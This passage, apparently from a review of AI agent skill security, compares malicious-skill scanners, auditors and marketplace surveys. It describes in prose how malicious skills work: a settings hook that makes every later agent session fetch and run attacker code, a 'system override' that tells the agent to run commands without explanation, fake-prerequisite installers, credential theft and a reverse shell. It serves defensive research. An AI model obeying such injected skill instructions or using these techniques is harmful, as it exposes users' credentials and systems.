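| Sentry Skill Scanner (static) | Rules | 67.3% | 28.7% | 548 |
| Snyk Agent Scan | Rules | 93.2% | 28.7% | 82 |
| VirusTotal | Many antivirus engines | 99.5% | 21.6% | 4 |
| Panguard Skill Auditor (static) | Rules | 76.2% | 18.6% | 229 |
| SkillScan | Rules | 70.0% | 14.5% | 244 |
| Skill Security Scan | Rules | 28.5% | 8.7% | 858 |

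None of these scanners uses a permission lattice. Guo and colleagues cite Bhardwaj's paper but didn't run SkillFortify, so their results can't show whether it would match its 92.6 percent recall on skills that Bhardwaj didn't generate. The rule-based scanners are the nearest comparison, since SkillFortify made all of its detections by matching patterns. Most of these rule-based scanners missed well over half of the malicious skills, and the one that caught 84 percent also flagged 64 percent of the benign ones.

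Adding a language model raised Sentry's recall from 28.7 to 98.4 percent and Cisco's from 35.6 to 92.7 percent, but it also raised the number of false alarms. Sentry wrongly flagged 937 benign skills, or 23 percent of them. Precision is higher in this benchmark than it would be in use because half the collection is malicious. In a marketplace where one skill in 100 is malicious, only one in 25 skills flagged by a scanner with Sentry's error rates would be malicious.

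Most scanners had more trouble detecting attacks in instructions than attacks in code. AI-Infra-Guard caught 99.2 percent of the attacks in code but 74.8 percent of those in instructions, and only 35.8 percent of the skills that get the agent to put biased or false content in its answers. Sentry's full mode was the exception, with 97.6 percent recall on the instruction attacks, although Guo and colleagues write in their abstract that the strongest detector "collapses" on prompt injection.

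Guo and colleagues also tested 11 tools built for other jobs, five to detect malicious software packages and six to stop prompt injection. Attention Tracker flagged every skill in the collection. GuardDog raised only 49 false alarms but caught 15.4 percent of the malicious skills. Combining the two kinds of tool didn't help much. They argue that each kind examines only half of a skill, and that neither can determine whether the skill's actions match its advertised task.

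### The 703 skills found in the wild

To collect the wild sample, Guo and colleagues started from public reports of malicious skills, looked for other skills by the same accounts, and recovered deleted ones from version histories. Two researchers then read every skill. The sample is much less varied than its size suggests, because two accounts published 569 of the 703 skills, and 607 skills used the same trick of telling the user or agent to install a fake prerequisite first. In Koi's audit, nearly all the malicious skills also relied on a download from somewhere else.

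The wild sample is narrow, which distorts any comparison based on it. VirusTotal caught 87.9 percent of the wild skills, which alone would make it look like one of the best skill scanners available, but it caught only 21.6 percent of the full collection. The rates differ because antivirus engines recognise the delivered malware. VirusTotal found 99.3 percent of the wild skills that delivered malware, but 9.1 percent of those that stole credentials directly.

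If a skill's instructions include a fake prerequisite, a containment check could detect at most a web address or a shell command, which the instructions of many harmless skills also contain.

Twelve of the wild skills attacked the agent itself. One case Guo and colleagues describe is `project-init`, whose setup script adds a hook to `.claude/settings.json`. Every later agent session then fetches and runs the attacker's code, even if the user never calls the skill again. Setting up a project normally involves writing files, so the skill could plausibly declare filesystem WRITE. The four-level lattice would then accept the change to the settings file, but a manifest that listed permitted paths would reveal it. Another skill, `autonomous-mobile-builder`, opens with a "system override" that tells the agent to explain nothing and only run the commands provided. The override is plain text, and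 no capability on the lattice corresponds to it.

### Checking a skill against its own description

*Semia* (Wen, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes an auditor that looks for safeguards that are missing or are stated only in the skill's prose. Its example, `clawnads`, is a published skill that gives an agent a cryptocurrency wallet. The skill's instructions require the operator's approval for transfers to outside wallets, but let transfers to other agents go through at once. An attacker can therefore message the agent and ask it to move $500 to "my agent account".

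Semia uses a language model to translate the whole skill into simple facts, such as that an outside message can trigger the signing action and that this action signs a transaction. One check rejects facts that don't fit together. Another turns the facts back into English and measures how much the result differs from the original text. The model revises its translation until both checks pass or it runs out of attempts. Semia then queries the facts in Datalog, a language for logical deduction. For `clawnads`, it finds a path from an outside message to a signed transaction with no approval step.

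On 541 skills labelled by experts, Semia had a precision of 84.5 percent and a recall of 97.7 percent. These figures aren't comparable with the MalSkillBench ones, because the experts labelled both malicious skills and benign ones that had exploitable flaws. When Wen and colleagues removed the translation into facts, the F1 score, which combines precision and recall, fell by 19.9 points from 90.6 percent. They also ran Semia on 13,728 published skills and found 17 previously unknown critical vulnerabilities. The maintainers of OpenClaw's registry confirmed all 17, which is probably the best evidence for the method because it came from outside the team.

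A Semia query always gives the same answer for the same facts, but a language model produces those facts. If the model leaves out the one sentence that lets outside messages reach the wallet, the query returns nothing. Semia therefore isn't sound in the sense a containment proof requires. It also never runs the skill, so a finding describes what could happen according to the facts.

*SKILLLITE* (Ou, Deng and colleagues, 2026) comes closer to comparing declared and actual behaviour. A small language model reads `SKILL.md` and writes down the skill's purpose and the capabilities it would reasonably need. Separate analysers, which use no language model, list the sensitive operations they find in the files. The model then judges whether the purpose justifies those operations. For example, opening network connections would look suspicious in a document formatter but not in a deployment tool.

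SKILLLITE scored an F1 of 90.5 percent on MalSkillBench, slightly above the 88.6 percent that Guo and colleagues report for Sentry's full mode. On a set of malicious skills collected from real marketplaces, SKILLLITE scored 80.7 percent. It compares a model's estimate of what a skill should need with analysers' predictions of what its files would do. Ou and colleagues explicitly exclude behaviour that appears only when the skill runs.

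Bühler and colleagues similarly compared AgentBound's generated manifests for MCP servers with handwritten ones. Both sets of manifests again came from reading the code. Guo and colleagues also cite a semantic-fuzzing method for finding skills that violate their own specifications.

### How to test containment

A direct test would run real skills, record every resource they use, and compare the record with the inferred set. Before the runs, the analyser produces an inferred set I for each skill. The tester then runs the skill on several inputs and joins everything it was seen to do into an observed set O. If

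O ⋢ I

then the analyser missed something. The result doesn't depend on anyone's opinion about whether the skill is malicious. It doesn't need a declared set either, which matters because most published skills have none.

Suppose the analyser infers filesystem READ for a chart script, but the record shows that the script also created a temporary file. O therefore includes filesystem WRITE, and the tester counts a miss. A malware benchmark would score the analyser as correct for passing the skill, because the skill is harmless.

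Most of the record could come from `strace`, which Guo and colleagues have already used with skills:

| What the skill does | How the test detects it | Capability in O |
|---|---|---|
| Opens a file for reading | `openat` call | filesystem READ |
| Creates, changes or deletes a file | `openat` for writing, `unlink` | filesystem WRITE |
| Changes who may use a file | `chmod` call | filesystem ADMIN |
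| Contacts a server | `connect` call, plus a proxy that decrypts the traffic | network READ or WRITE |
| Starts another program | `execve` call | shell WRITE |
| Reads an environment variable | A modified Python or Node interpreter | environment READ |

Environment variables need separate treatment because a program receives them in memory when it starts and can read them without making a system call. The tester also has to separate the skill's actions from the rest of the record. Python opens dozens of its own library files before the first line of a script runs, so the tester should first record a run of an empty script and subtract the files it opens. The agent also reads and writes files, so the tester should count only actions by the script's process and the processes it starts.

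An analyser that inferred only shell WRITE misses any file that a child process such as `scp` opens, unless it applies the closure rule for the shell. The tester should count misses with and without that rule to show how much of the protection depends on it.

Bhardwaj's soundness theorem covers only the operations that his software extracts from a skill. If a script assembles a command from pieces of text while it runs, he treats the command as outside the theorem, not as a counterexample. That is a fair way to state a theorem, but the user's files are equally exposed either way. A test should count these misses and report them separately to show how much real behaviour the guarantee doesn't cover.

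An analyser could avoid every miss by always inferring top, so the test also needs a measure of excess. One simple measure is the number of levels by which I exceeds O, summed over the eight resource types, which gives a total from 0 to 24. Some of this excess would come from code that the test runs never reached, so the total is only an upper limit on the analyser's overestimate.

When a skill declares a set D, the same runs also test containment. If I ⊑ D but O ⋢ D, the check approved a skill that exceeded its declaration, and a single confirmed case would show that the guarantee doesn't hold in practice. If I ⋢ D but O ⊑ D, the analyser may have raised a false alarm, or the inputs may not have triggered the behaviour it predicted.

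Much of the material already exists. SkillFortify has a `verify` command that reports a skill's inferred set, and MalSkillBench includes 1,914 generated skills with attacks wholly or partly in code, which Guo and colleagues ran under `strace`. Comparing the inferred sets with the traces would be an easy first test, although the runs would also need to record environment variables and network traffic. The 4,000 popular ClawHub skills would make a better sample for estimating how often the analyser misses something in ordinary use, but many of them would need working accounts, or convincing imitations of the services they contact, before their scripts did anything worth measuring.

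If the tester ran 300 randomly chosen skills and found no misses, they could be 95 percent confident that fewer than about 1 percent of skills have a miss that such runs can reveal. The true share could be higher, because a test run covers only some of a script's branches. A malicious script could also check whether `strace` is attached and avoid harmful actions while it is.

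## What studies of published skills show

Depending on the survey, between 0.1 and 26 percent of published skills are dangerous. The surveys count different things, and none of these rates measures how often skills exceed their declared permissions. But the surveys also report much of what a marketplace would want to know before running a containment check on every skill, such as how many skills contain scripts, declare permissions or use a shell.

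### From suspicious patterns to confirmed attacks

The earliest survey, *Agent Skills in the Wild* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026), reports the highest share of skills with at least one "vulnerability", 26.1 percent. It collected 42,447 skills from two marketplaces, skills.rest and skillsmp.com, in December 2025, and kept 31,132 after dropping duplicates, very short skills, skills not in English and skills whose repositories had disappeared. One scanner searched the instructions and scripts for suspicious text, such as a command that reads a password file, and other scanners looked for hidden or manipulative instructions. Claude 3.5 Sonnet then judged the 12,847 skills that any scanner had flagged, and the survey counted 8,126 of them as vulnerable.

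Liu, Wang and colleagues flag skills for malicious code, careless code and anything else that could enable harm. They define 14 patterns in four groups: prompt injection, sending data out, gaining extra privileges, and supply-chain risks such as running downloaded code. Almost half of the flagged skills had only low-severity patterns, such as a software dependency without a fixed version number. Of all the skills studied, 5.2 percent had a high-severity pattern, which the researchers say strongly suggests malicious intent. But when they reviewed the 87 riskiest skills by hand, they found clear signs of malice in only 23.

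Their detector did fairly well on 200 skills that two researchers had labelled. It flagged 60, of which 52 were vulnerable (a precision of 86.7 percent), and it missed 11 of the 63 vulnerable ones (a recall of 82.5 percent). The stated margin of error on the precision is 4.7 percentage points, which would be right for 200 flagged skills, but for 60 it is nearer 9. The labels also use the same broad definition of a vulnerability, so these figures don't measure how well the detector recognises malware.

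In *Do Not Mention This to the User*, Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026), an overlapping team, looked for confirmed attacks among 98,380 skills collected from the same two marketplaces a month later. They used text patterns and GPT-5.2 to narrow these down to 4,287 candidates. They then ran each candidate in a container baited with fake API keys and login keys, and recorded its network traffic, system calls and file changes. Of the candidates, 762 behaved suspiciously. Two researchers reviewed those and confirmed 157 as malicious, with a total of 632 vulnerabilities, an average of four each. The marketplaces removed all 157.

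Beurer-Kellner and colleagues at the security company Snyk report that they confirmed 76 malicious skills on ClawHub by hand. They also report that their scanner raised at least one critical alert on 534 of 3,984 skills, seven times as many.

*Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (Etteib, Lunghi and Bissyandé, 2026) describes the largest scan, which covered 134,934 skills from three marketplaces for about $34. It used attention, the weights that set how much each part of a text influences a language model's next word. An injected instruction can work only if the model attends to it, so the researchers ran a small model on each skill and ranked the passages by the attention they received. A larger model then assessed the top five. Two of the researchers reviewed 359 flagged skills and found 131 malicious ones, 80 offensive security tools and 27 false alarms, but couldn't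 agree on the other 121. The reported precision of 83 percent leaves out the security tools and the disputed skills. If all the disputed skills were harmless, it would be 47 percent. Of the 131 malicious skills, 22 were flagged only in a comparison run in which the larger model read each skill in full.

*Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026), the most recent of these surveys, assesses malice and capability separately. The researchers examined 6,309 listings from skillsmp.com and ClawHub in July and August 2026. Their scanner used Claude models to read every file in each skill, and an agent ran nearly all of the skills in a sandbox. The scanner belongs to Metano Labs, where three of the researchers work, and nobody outside has evaluated it.

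| Survey | What it counted | Skills examined | Count | Share |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Liu, Wang and colleagues | Any of 14 risky patterns | 31,132 | 8,126 | 26.1% |
| Beurer-Kellner and colleagues | Critical alerts from a scanner | 3,984 | 534 | 13.4% |
| Pandey and colleagues | A verdict of malicious or suspicious | 6,309 | 338 | 5.4% |
| Liu, Wang and colleagues | High-severity patterns | 31,132 | 1,619 | 5.2% |
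| Beurer-Kellner and colleagues | Attacks confirmed by hand | 3,984 | 76 | 1.9% |
| Liu, Chen and colleagues | Attacks confirmed in a sandbox and by hand | 98,380 | 157 | 0.16% |
| Etteib and colleagues | Attacks confirmed by hand | 134,934 | 131 | 0.10% |

The estimates differ mostly because some count suspected malicious skills and others count only confirmed ones. The 5.2 percent and 0.16 percent figures describe the same two marketplaces a month apart. The first is about thirty times the second because a pattern that "strongly suggests" malice usually turns out to be something else. Security tools are a common example, making up about a third of the skills in which Pandey and colleagues found any sign of a threat. Etteib and colleagues classify them separately.

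Timing and method probably account for the rest of the difference. On ClawHub alone, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues confirmed 1.9 percent of skills as malicious, while Etteib and colleagues confirmed 0.16 percent. The first team used a historical copy of the marketplace, including deleted skills, from around the time of the ClawHavoc campaign. The second team scanned ClawHub when it was much larger and set its detection threshold to avoid false alarms. At that threshold, its scanner caught only 11 of 21 planted attacks in a laboratory test.

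### Most skills have nothing for a script analyser to read

Liu, Wang and colleagues report that 11.5 percent of skills come with scripts, but their count is a little uncertain because they give 3,574 as both the number of scripts and the number of skills that have them. *SkillsBench* (2026) reports that 59.9 percent of skills in a much larger collection of 767,430 contain only a `SKILL.md` file, so at most about 40 percent could have a separate script. Scripts can be more common in curated libraries. *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026) describes one in which 105 of 163 skills have files in a scripts folder, most of them in Python.

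An analyser that reads only scripts would therefore infer bottom for most published skills and pass them all. Yet Liu, Wang and colleagues flagged 24.2 percent of skills without scripts, compared with 40.6 percent of those with scripts. They write that scripts make a vulnerability 2.12 times as likely, but 2.12 is the odds ratio, and the ratio of the two rates is 1.7. Skills without scripts are so much more common that they make up about 6,700 of the 8,126 flagged skills, or 82 percent.

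Many of these skills include commands in their written instructions. *Inside the Skill Market* (2026) found commands in the `SKILL.md` of 79.3 percent of software-engineering skills. *@skills* (2026) found blocks of shell commands in 60 percent of 569 skills that companies such as Amazon, Google and Cloudflare publish for their own products. A company with a command-line program can write one skill that explains it, and any agent with a shell can then use the product.

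An analyser could extract these blocks and treat them as scripts. It would catch more that way, but the result would no longer be a bound, because the model fills in the file names, may change the command, and may write a different one if the first fails. To hold such a skill to its declared set, the agent's software has to check each command as the model issues it.

### Few skills declare anything, and the lists seldom match

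For declarations, the best figures come from Pandey and colleagues. Of 6,061 listings with a readable header, 770 (12.7 percent) fill in `allowed-tools`, the standard's only permission field. The researchers compared each list with the capabilities their scanner inferred from the files, using five classes that both could express:

| Comparison with the inferred capabilities | Listings | Share of the 770 |
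|---|---|---|
| The list matches | 166 | 22% |
| It only leaves something out | 300 | 39% |
| It only includes something extra | 147 | 19% |
| It does both | 157 | 20% |

So fewer than 3 percent of the listings with a readable header have a list that matches their files. Authors fill in the field more often on ClawHub than on skillsmp.com (17.7 percent against 9.9), but 88 percent of the ClawHub lists leave something out, compared with 31 percent on skillsmp.com.

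A containment check fails only on omissions, because I ⊑ D still holds when an author declares too much. By that standard, 313 of the 770 lists are adequate. Suppose a strict marketplace treated a missing declaration as bottom. The scanner found at least one significant capability, such as shell or credential access, in 4,431 of the 6,309 listings, and at most 313 of those have declarations that cover what it found. At least 4,118 listings, or about two thirds of the total, would fail, although the same scanner classified only 338 as malicious or suspicious. A marketplace would have to get authors to write declarations long before it could enforce them.

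These figures may be unfair to skill authors. Since the field doesn't restrict a skill, leaving out the shell only keeps the approval request in place. Pandey and colleagues point out that on Android, where an app can't use a permission it hasn't requested, developers typically request too many. If skills had an enforced manifest, their authors would probably do the same, which would weaken the check without causing it to fail.

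The sandbox runs come closest to a direct test of containment. Among the listings with a declaration, 91 used at least one of the five classes while running, and 54 of those used a class they hadn't declared. This suggests O ⋢ D in more than half of the cases, but some of the recorded actions may have been the agent's own, because most skills ran only once, with no comparison run of the agent alone.

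### How often a sound analyser would have to give up

Pandey and colleagues found evidence of shell use in half of all listings, file reading in 35 percent, file writing and outgoing network access in 31 percent each, and access to credentials in 13 percent. These categories directly cover three of the lattice's eight resource types, namely filesystem, network and shell. Credentials don't correspond to a single type, because a skill may find them in the environment or in a file. The clipboard, browser and database types are not among these main categories.

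The shell figure matters most because, under the closure rule, shell WRITE raises every other entry, so a sound analyser would report nearly full access for about half of the listings. Far fewer than half of skills have scripts, so much of this shell use must come from commands in the prose. An analyser that reads only scripts therefore passes most skills without examining anything, while one that also reads the prose places half of them near top. Neither result would help a user much in choosing between two skills.

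The 50 percent figure comes from a language model's reading of the files, though, and the researchers couldn't confirm it by running the skills in a sandbox. They recorded a shell command in only 518 runs, about one in twelve. In the few cases where they also ran the agent without the skill, it still used a shell every time.

Dynamic evaluation, in which a program runs text as code, also forces a sound analyser to top when it can't work out the text. It is unclear how common this is in published skills. The scanner in *Agent Skills in the Wild* searched for `eval` and `exec`, but none of the 14 published patterns counts them. The nearest patterns are deliberately obscured code, found in 55 of 1,218 skills, and scripts that fetch and run other scripts, found in 67. Neither number can be used as a rate for the whole marketplace, because Liu, Wang and colleagues chose the 1,218 skills to include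 more of the rare problems.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues report that 2.9 percent of skills on ClawHub fetch code or instructions from elsewhere. Their example is a skill from moltbook.com, a social network for AI agents, that has the agent check for a new version every few hours and download new instructions. Whoever runs the site could change what every agent that uses the skill does, long after any review of the original files.

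Ordinary software packages create a milder form of the problem. Pandey and colleagues found that 2,871 listings depend on outside packages or repositories, and that 99 percent of those leave at least one without a fixed version. An analyser that has only the skill's folder must either treat a package's code as top or rely on a summary of what the package does, and a new version may make that summary wrong. The surveys don't report how much these groups overlap, so adding them up wouldn't give the share of skills for which a sound analyser would return top. None of the surveys ran such an analyser.

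### Where the attacks are

Of the 632 vulnerabilities in their 157 malicious skills, Liu, Chen and colleagues found 532 (84.2 percent) in `SKILL.md` and only 8.5 percent in Python, shell or JavaScript files. The rest were mostly in configuration files. Most of the vulnerabilities in `SKILL.md` must be commands, addresses and passwords that happen to be in the text, because overriding instructions, hidden directives and similar ways of manipulating the model account for only 209 vulnerabilities, a third of the total. The most common technique, used by 118 of the 157 skills, was to download a program and run it.

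One attacker produced 54.1 percent of those skills from a template, so the percentages partly reflect one person's habits. But other collections show a similar pattern. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues list three main techniques in the skills they confirmed. Two rely on installation instructions, which either link to malware or contain a disguised command that sends data out. Of the 82 malicious skills that Etteib and colleagues classed as hidden behind a harmless purpose, 34 were malicious installers and 35 stole credentials. Their method doesn't target separate script files, so it can't show what share of attacks is in scripts. Most skills in MalSkillBench's wild sample also required a fake prerequisite.

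Some skills do contain attacks in their scripts, such as `math-calculator`, which had a script that opened a reverse shell to the attacker's server. A calculator has no reason to use the network, so even the four-level lattice would have caught the script if the skill's author had declared no permissions.

A stock-analysis skill from the attention-based scan would be much harder to catch. It sends every request through a proxy server whose address and password are written in the skill's text. The attacker can read the user's queries and change the answers, yet the skill runs no shell command and opens no local file. Any stock tool would declare network access, so the lattice would not flag these requests. A sandbox that allowed connections only to the market-data provider would block the proxy.

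### Missed skills, installations and harm

All the confirmed counts are lower bounds, and the true totals are hard to estimate. Liu, Chen and colleagues re-examined 413 skills, a tenth of the candidates they hadn't confirmed, and found that 1.9 percent were attacks that needed more than one session to unfold. Scaled to all the unconfirmed candidates, that is about 80 malicious skills beyond the 157 confirmed. Another 93.2 percent of the sample contained triggers that had not gone off within the 60 seconds each test allowed. If one in ten of those triggers led to an attack, the same scaling would put the total at more than three times the 157. The researchers never ran the 94,093 skills that matched no suspicious pattern.

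Pandey and colleagues checked for misses more directly by reading 140 randomly chosen "benign" listings in full. They found no threats, which puts the miss rate at no more than about 2.1 percent with 95 percent confidence. Across their 5,971 benign listings, that could still mean up to about 125 missed threats, more than half as many as the 206 listings their scanner classified as malicious.

Deleted skills are also missing from the data. Liu, Wang and colleagues lost 7,353 skills, 17.3 percent of their collection, because the repositories were no longer available, and they suspect that malicious skills were overrepresented among them. The marketplaces' own scans don't fill these gaps, since many of the 26,502 ClawHub skills covered in *Red Skills or Blue Skills?* (2026) have incomplete safety records.

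The early rates may also be out of date. Skillsmp.com listed 15,082 skills in December 2025 and 73,193 a month later. By 6 June 2026 it listed 1,640,440, according to *Skills Are Not Islands* (2026).

A user's risk depends on which skills they install, but the surveys count every skill once. Downloads are very uneven. *SkVM* (2026) reports that 89 percent of 89,280 skills on skills.sh had fewer than 86 downloads, while a handful had between ten thousand and a million. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues raised no critical alerts on the 100 most used skills there, so a rate weighted by installations could be well below the rates in the table. The weighted rate could be higher on another marketplace, because the same researchers saw malicious skills on ClawHub with large download counts, though attackers can inflate these counts. *Agent Skills in the Wild* describes a backup skill with 2,847 downloads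 that collected API keys and Git credentials and sent them to a fixed outside address. Pandey and colleagues can't settle whether weighting would raise or lower the rate, because they deliberately left out both the most popular skills and the unused ones.

Download counts also miss copies. Gao, Baltes and colleagues (2026), in *From Registry to Repository*, matched 3,709 skills in software projects to originals on skills.sh. Most were nearly verbatim copies, and the projects rarely adopted later changes to the originals. When a marketplace deletes a malicious skill, the copies in people's projects remain.

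The evidence about harm is even weaker. Liu, Wang and colleagues ran 25 of the skills they were most confident about and found exploitable behaviour in 72 percent. Liu, Chen and colleagues observed skills stealing credentials, but these were fake credentials in containers. Such tests show that an attack works, but not how many people lost passwords or money. Researchers would need records from the attackers' servers or reports from victims to measure that, and none of these surveys had either.
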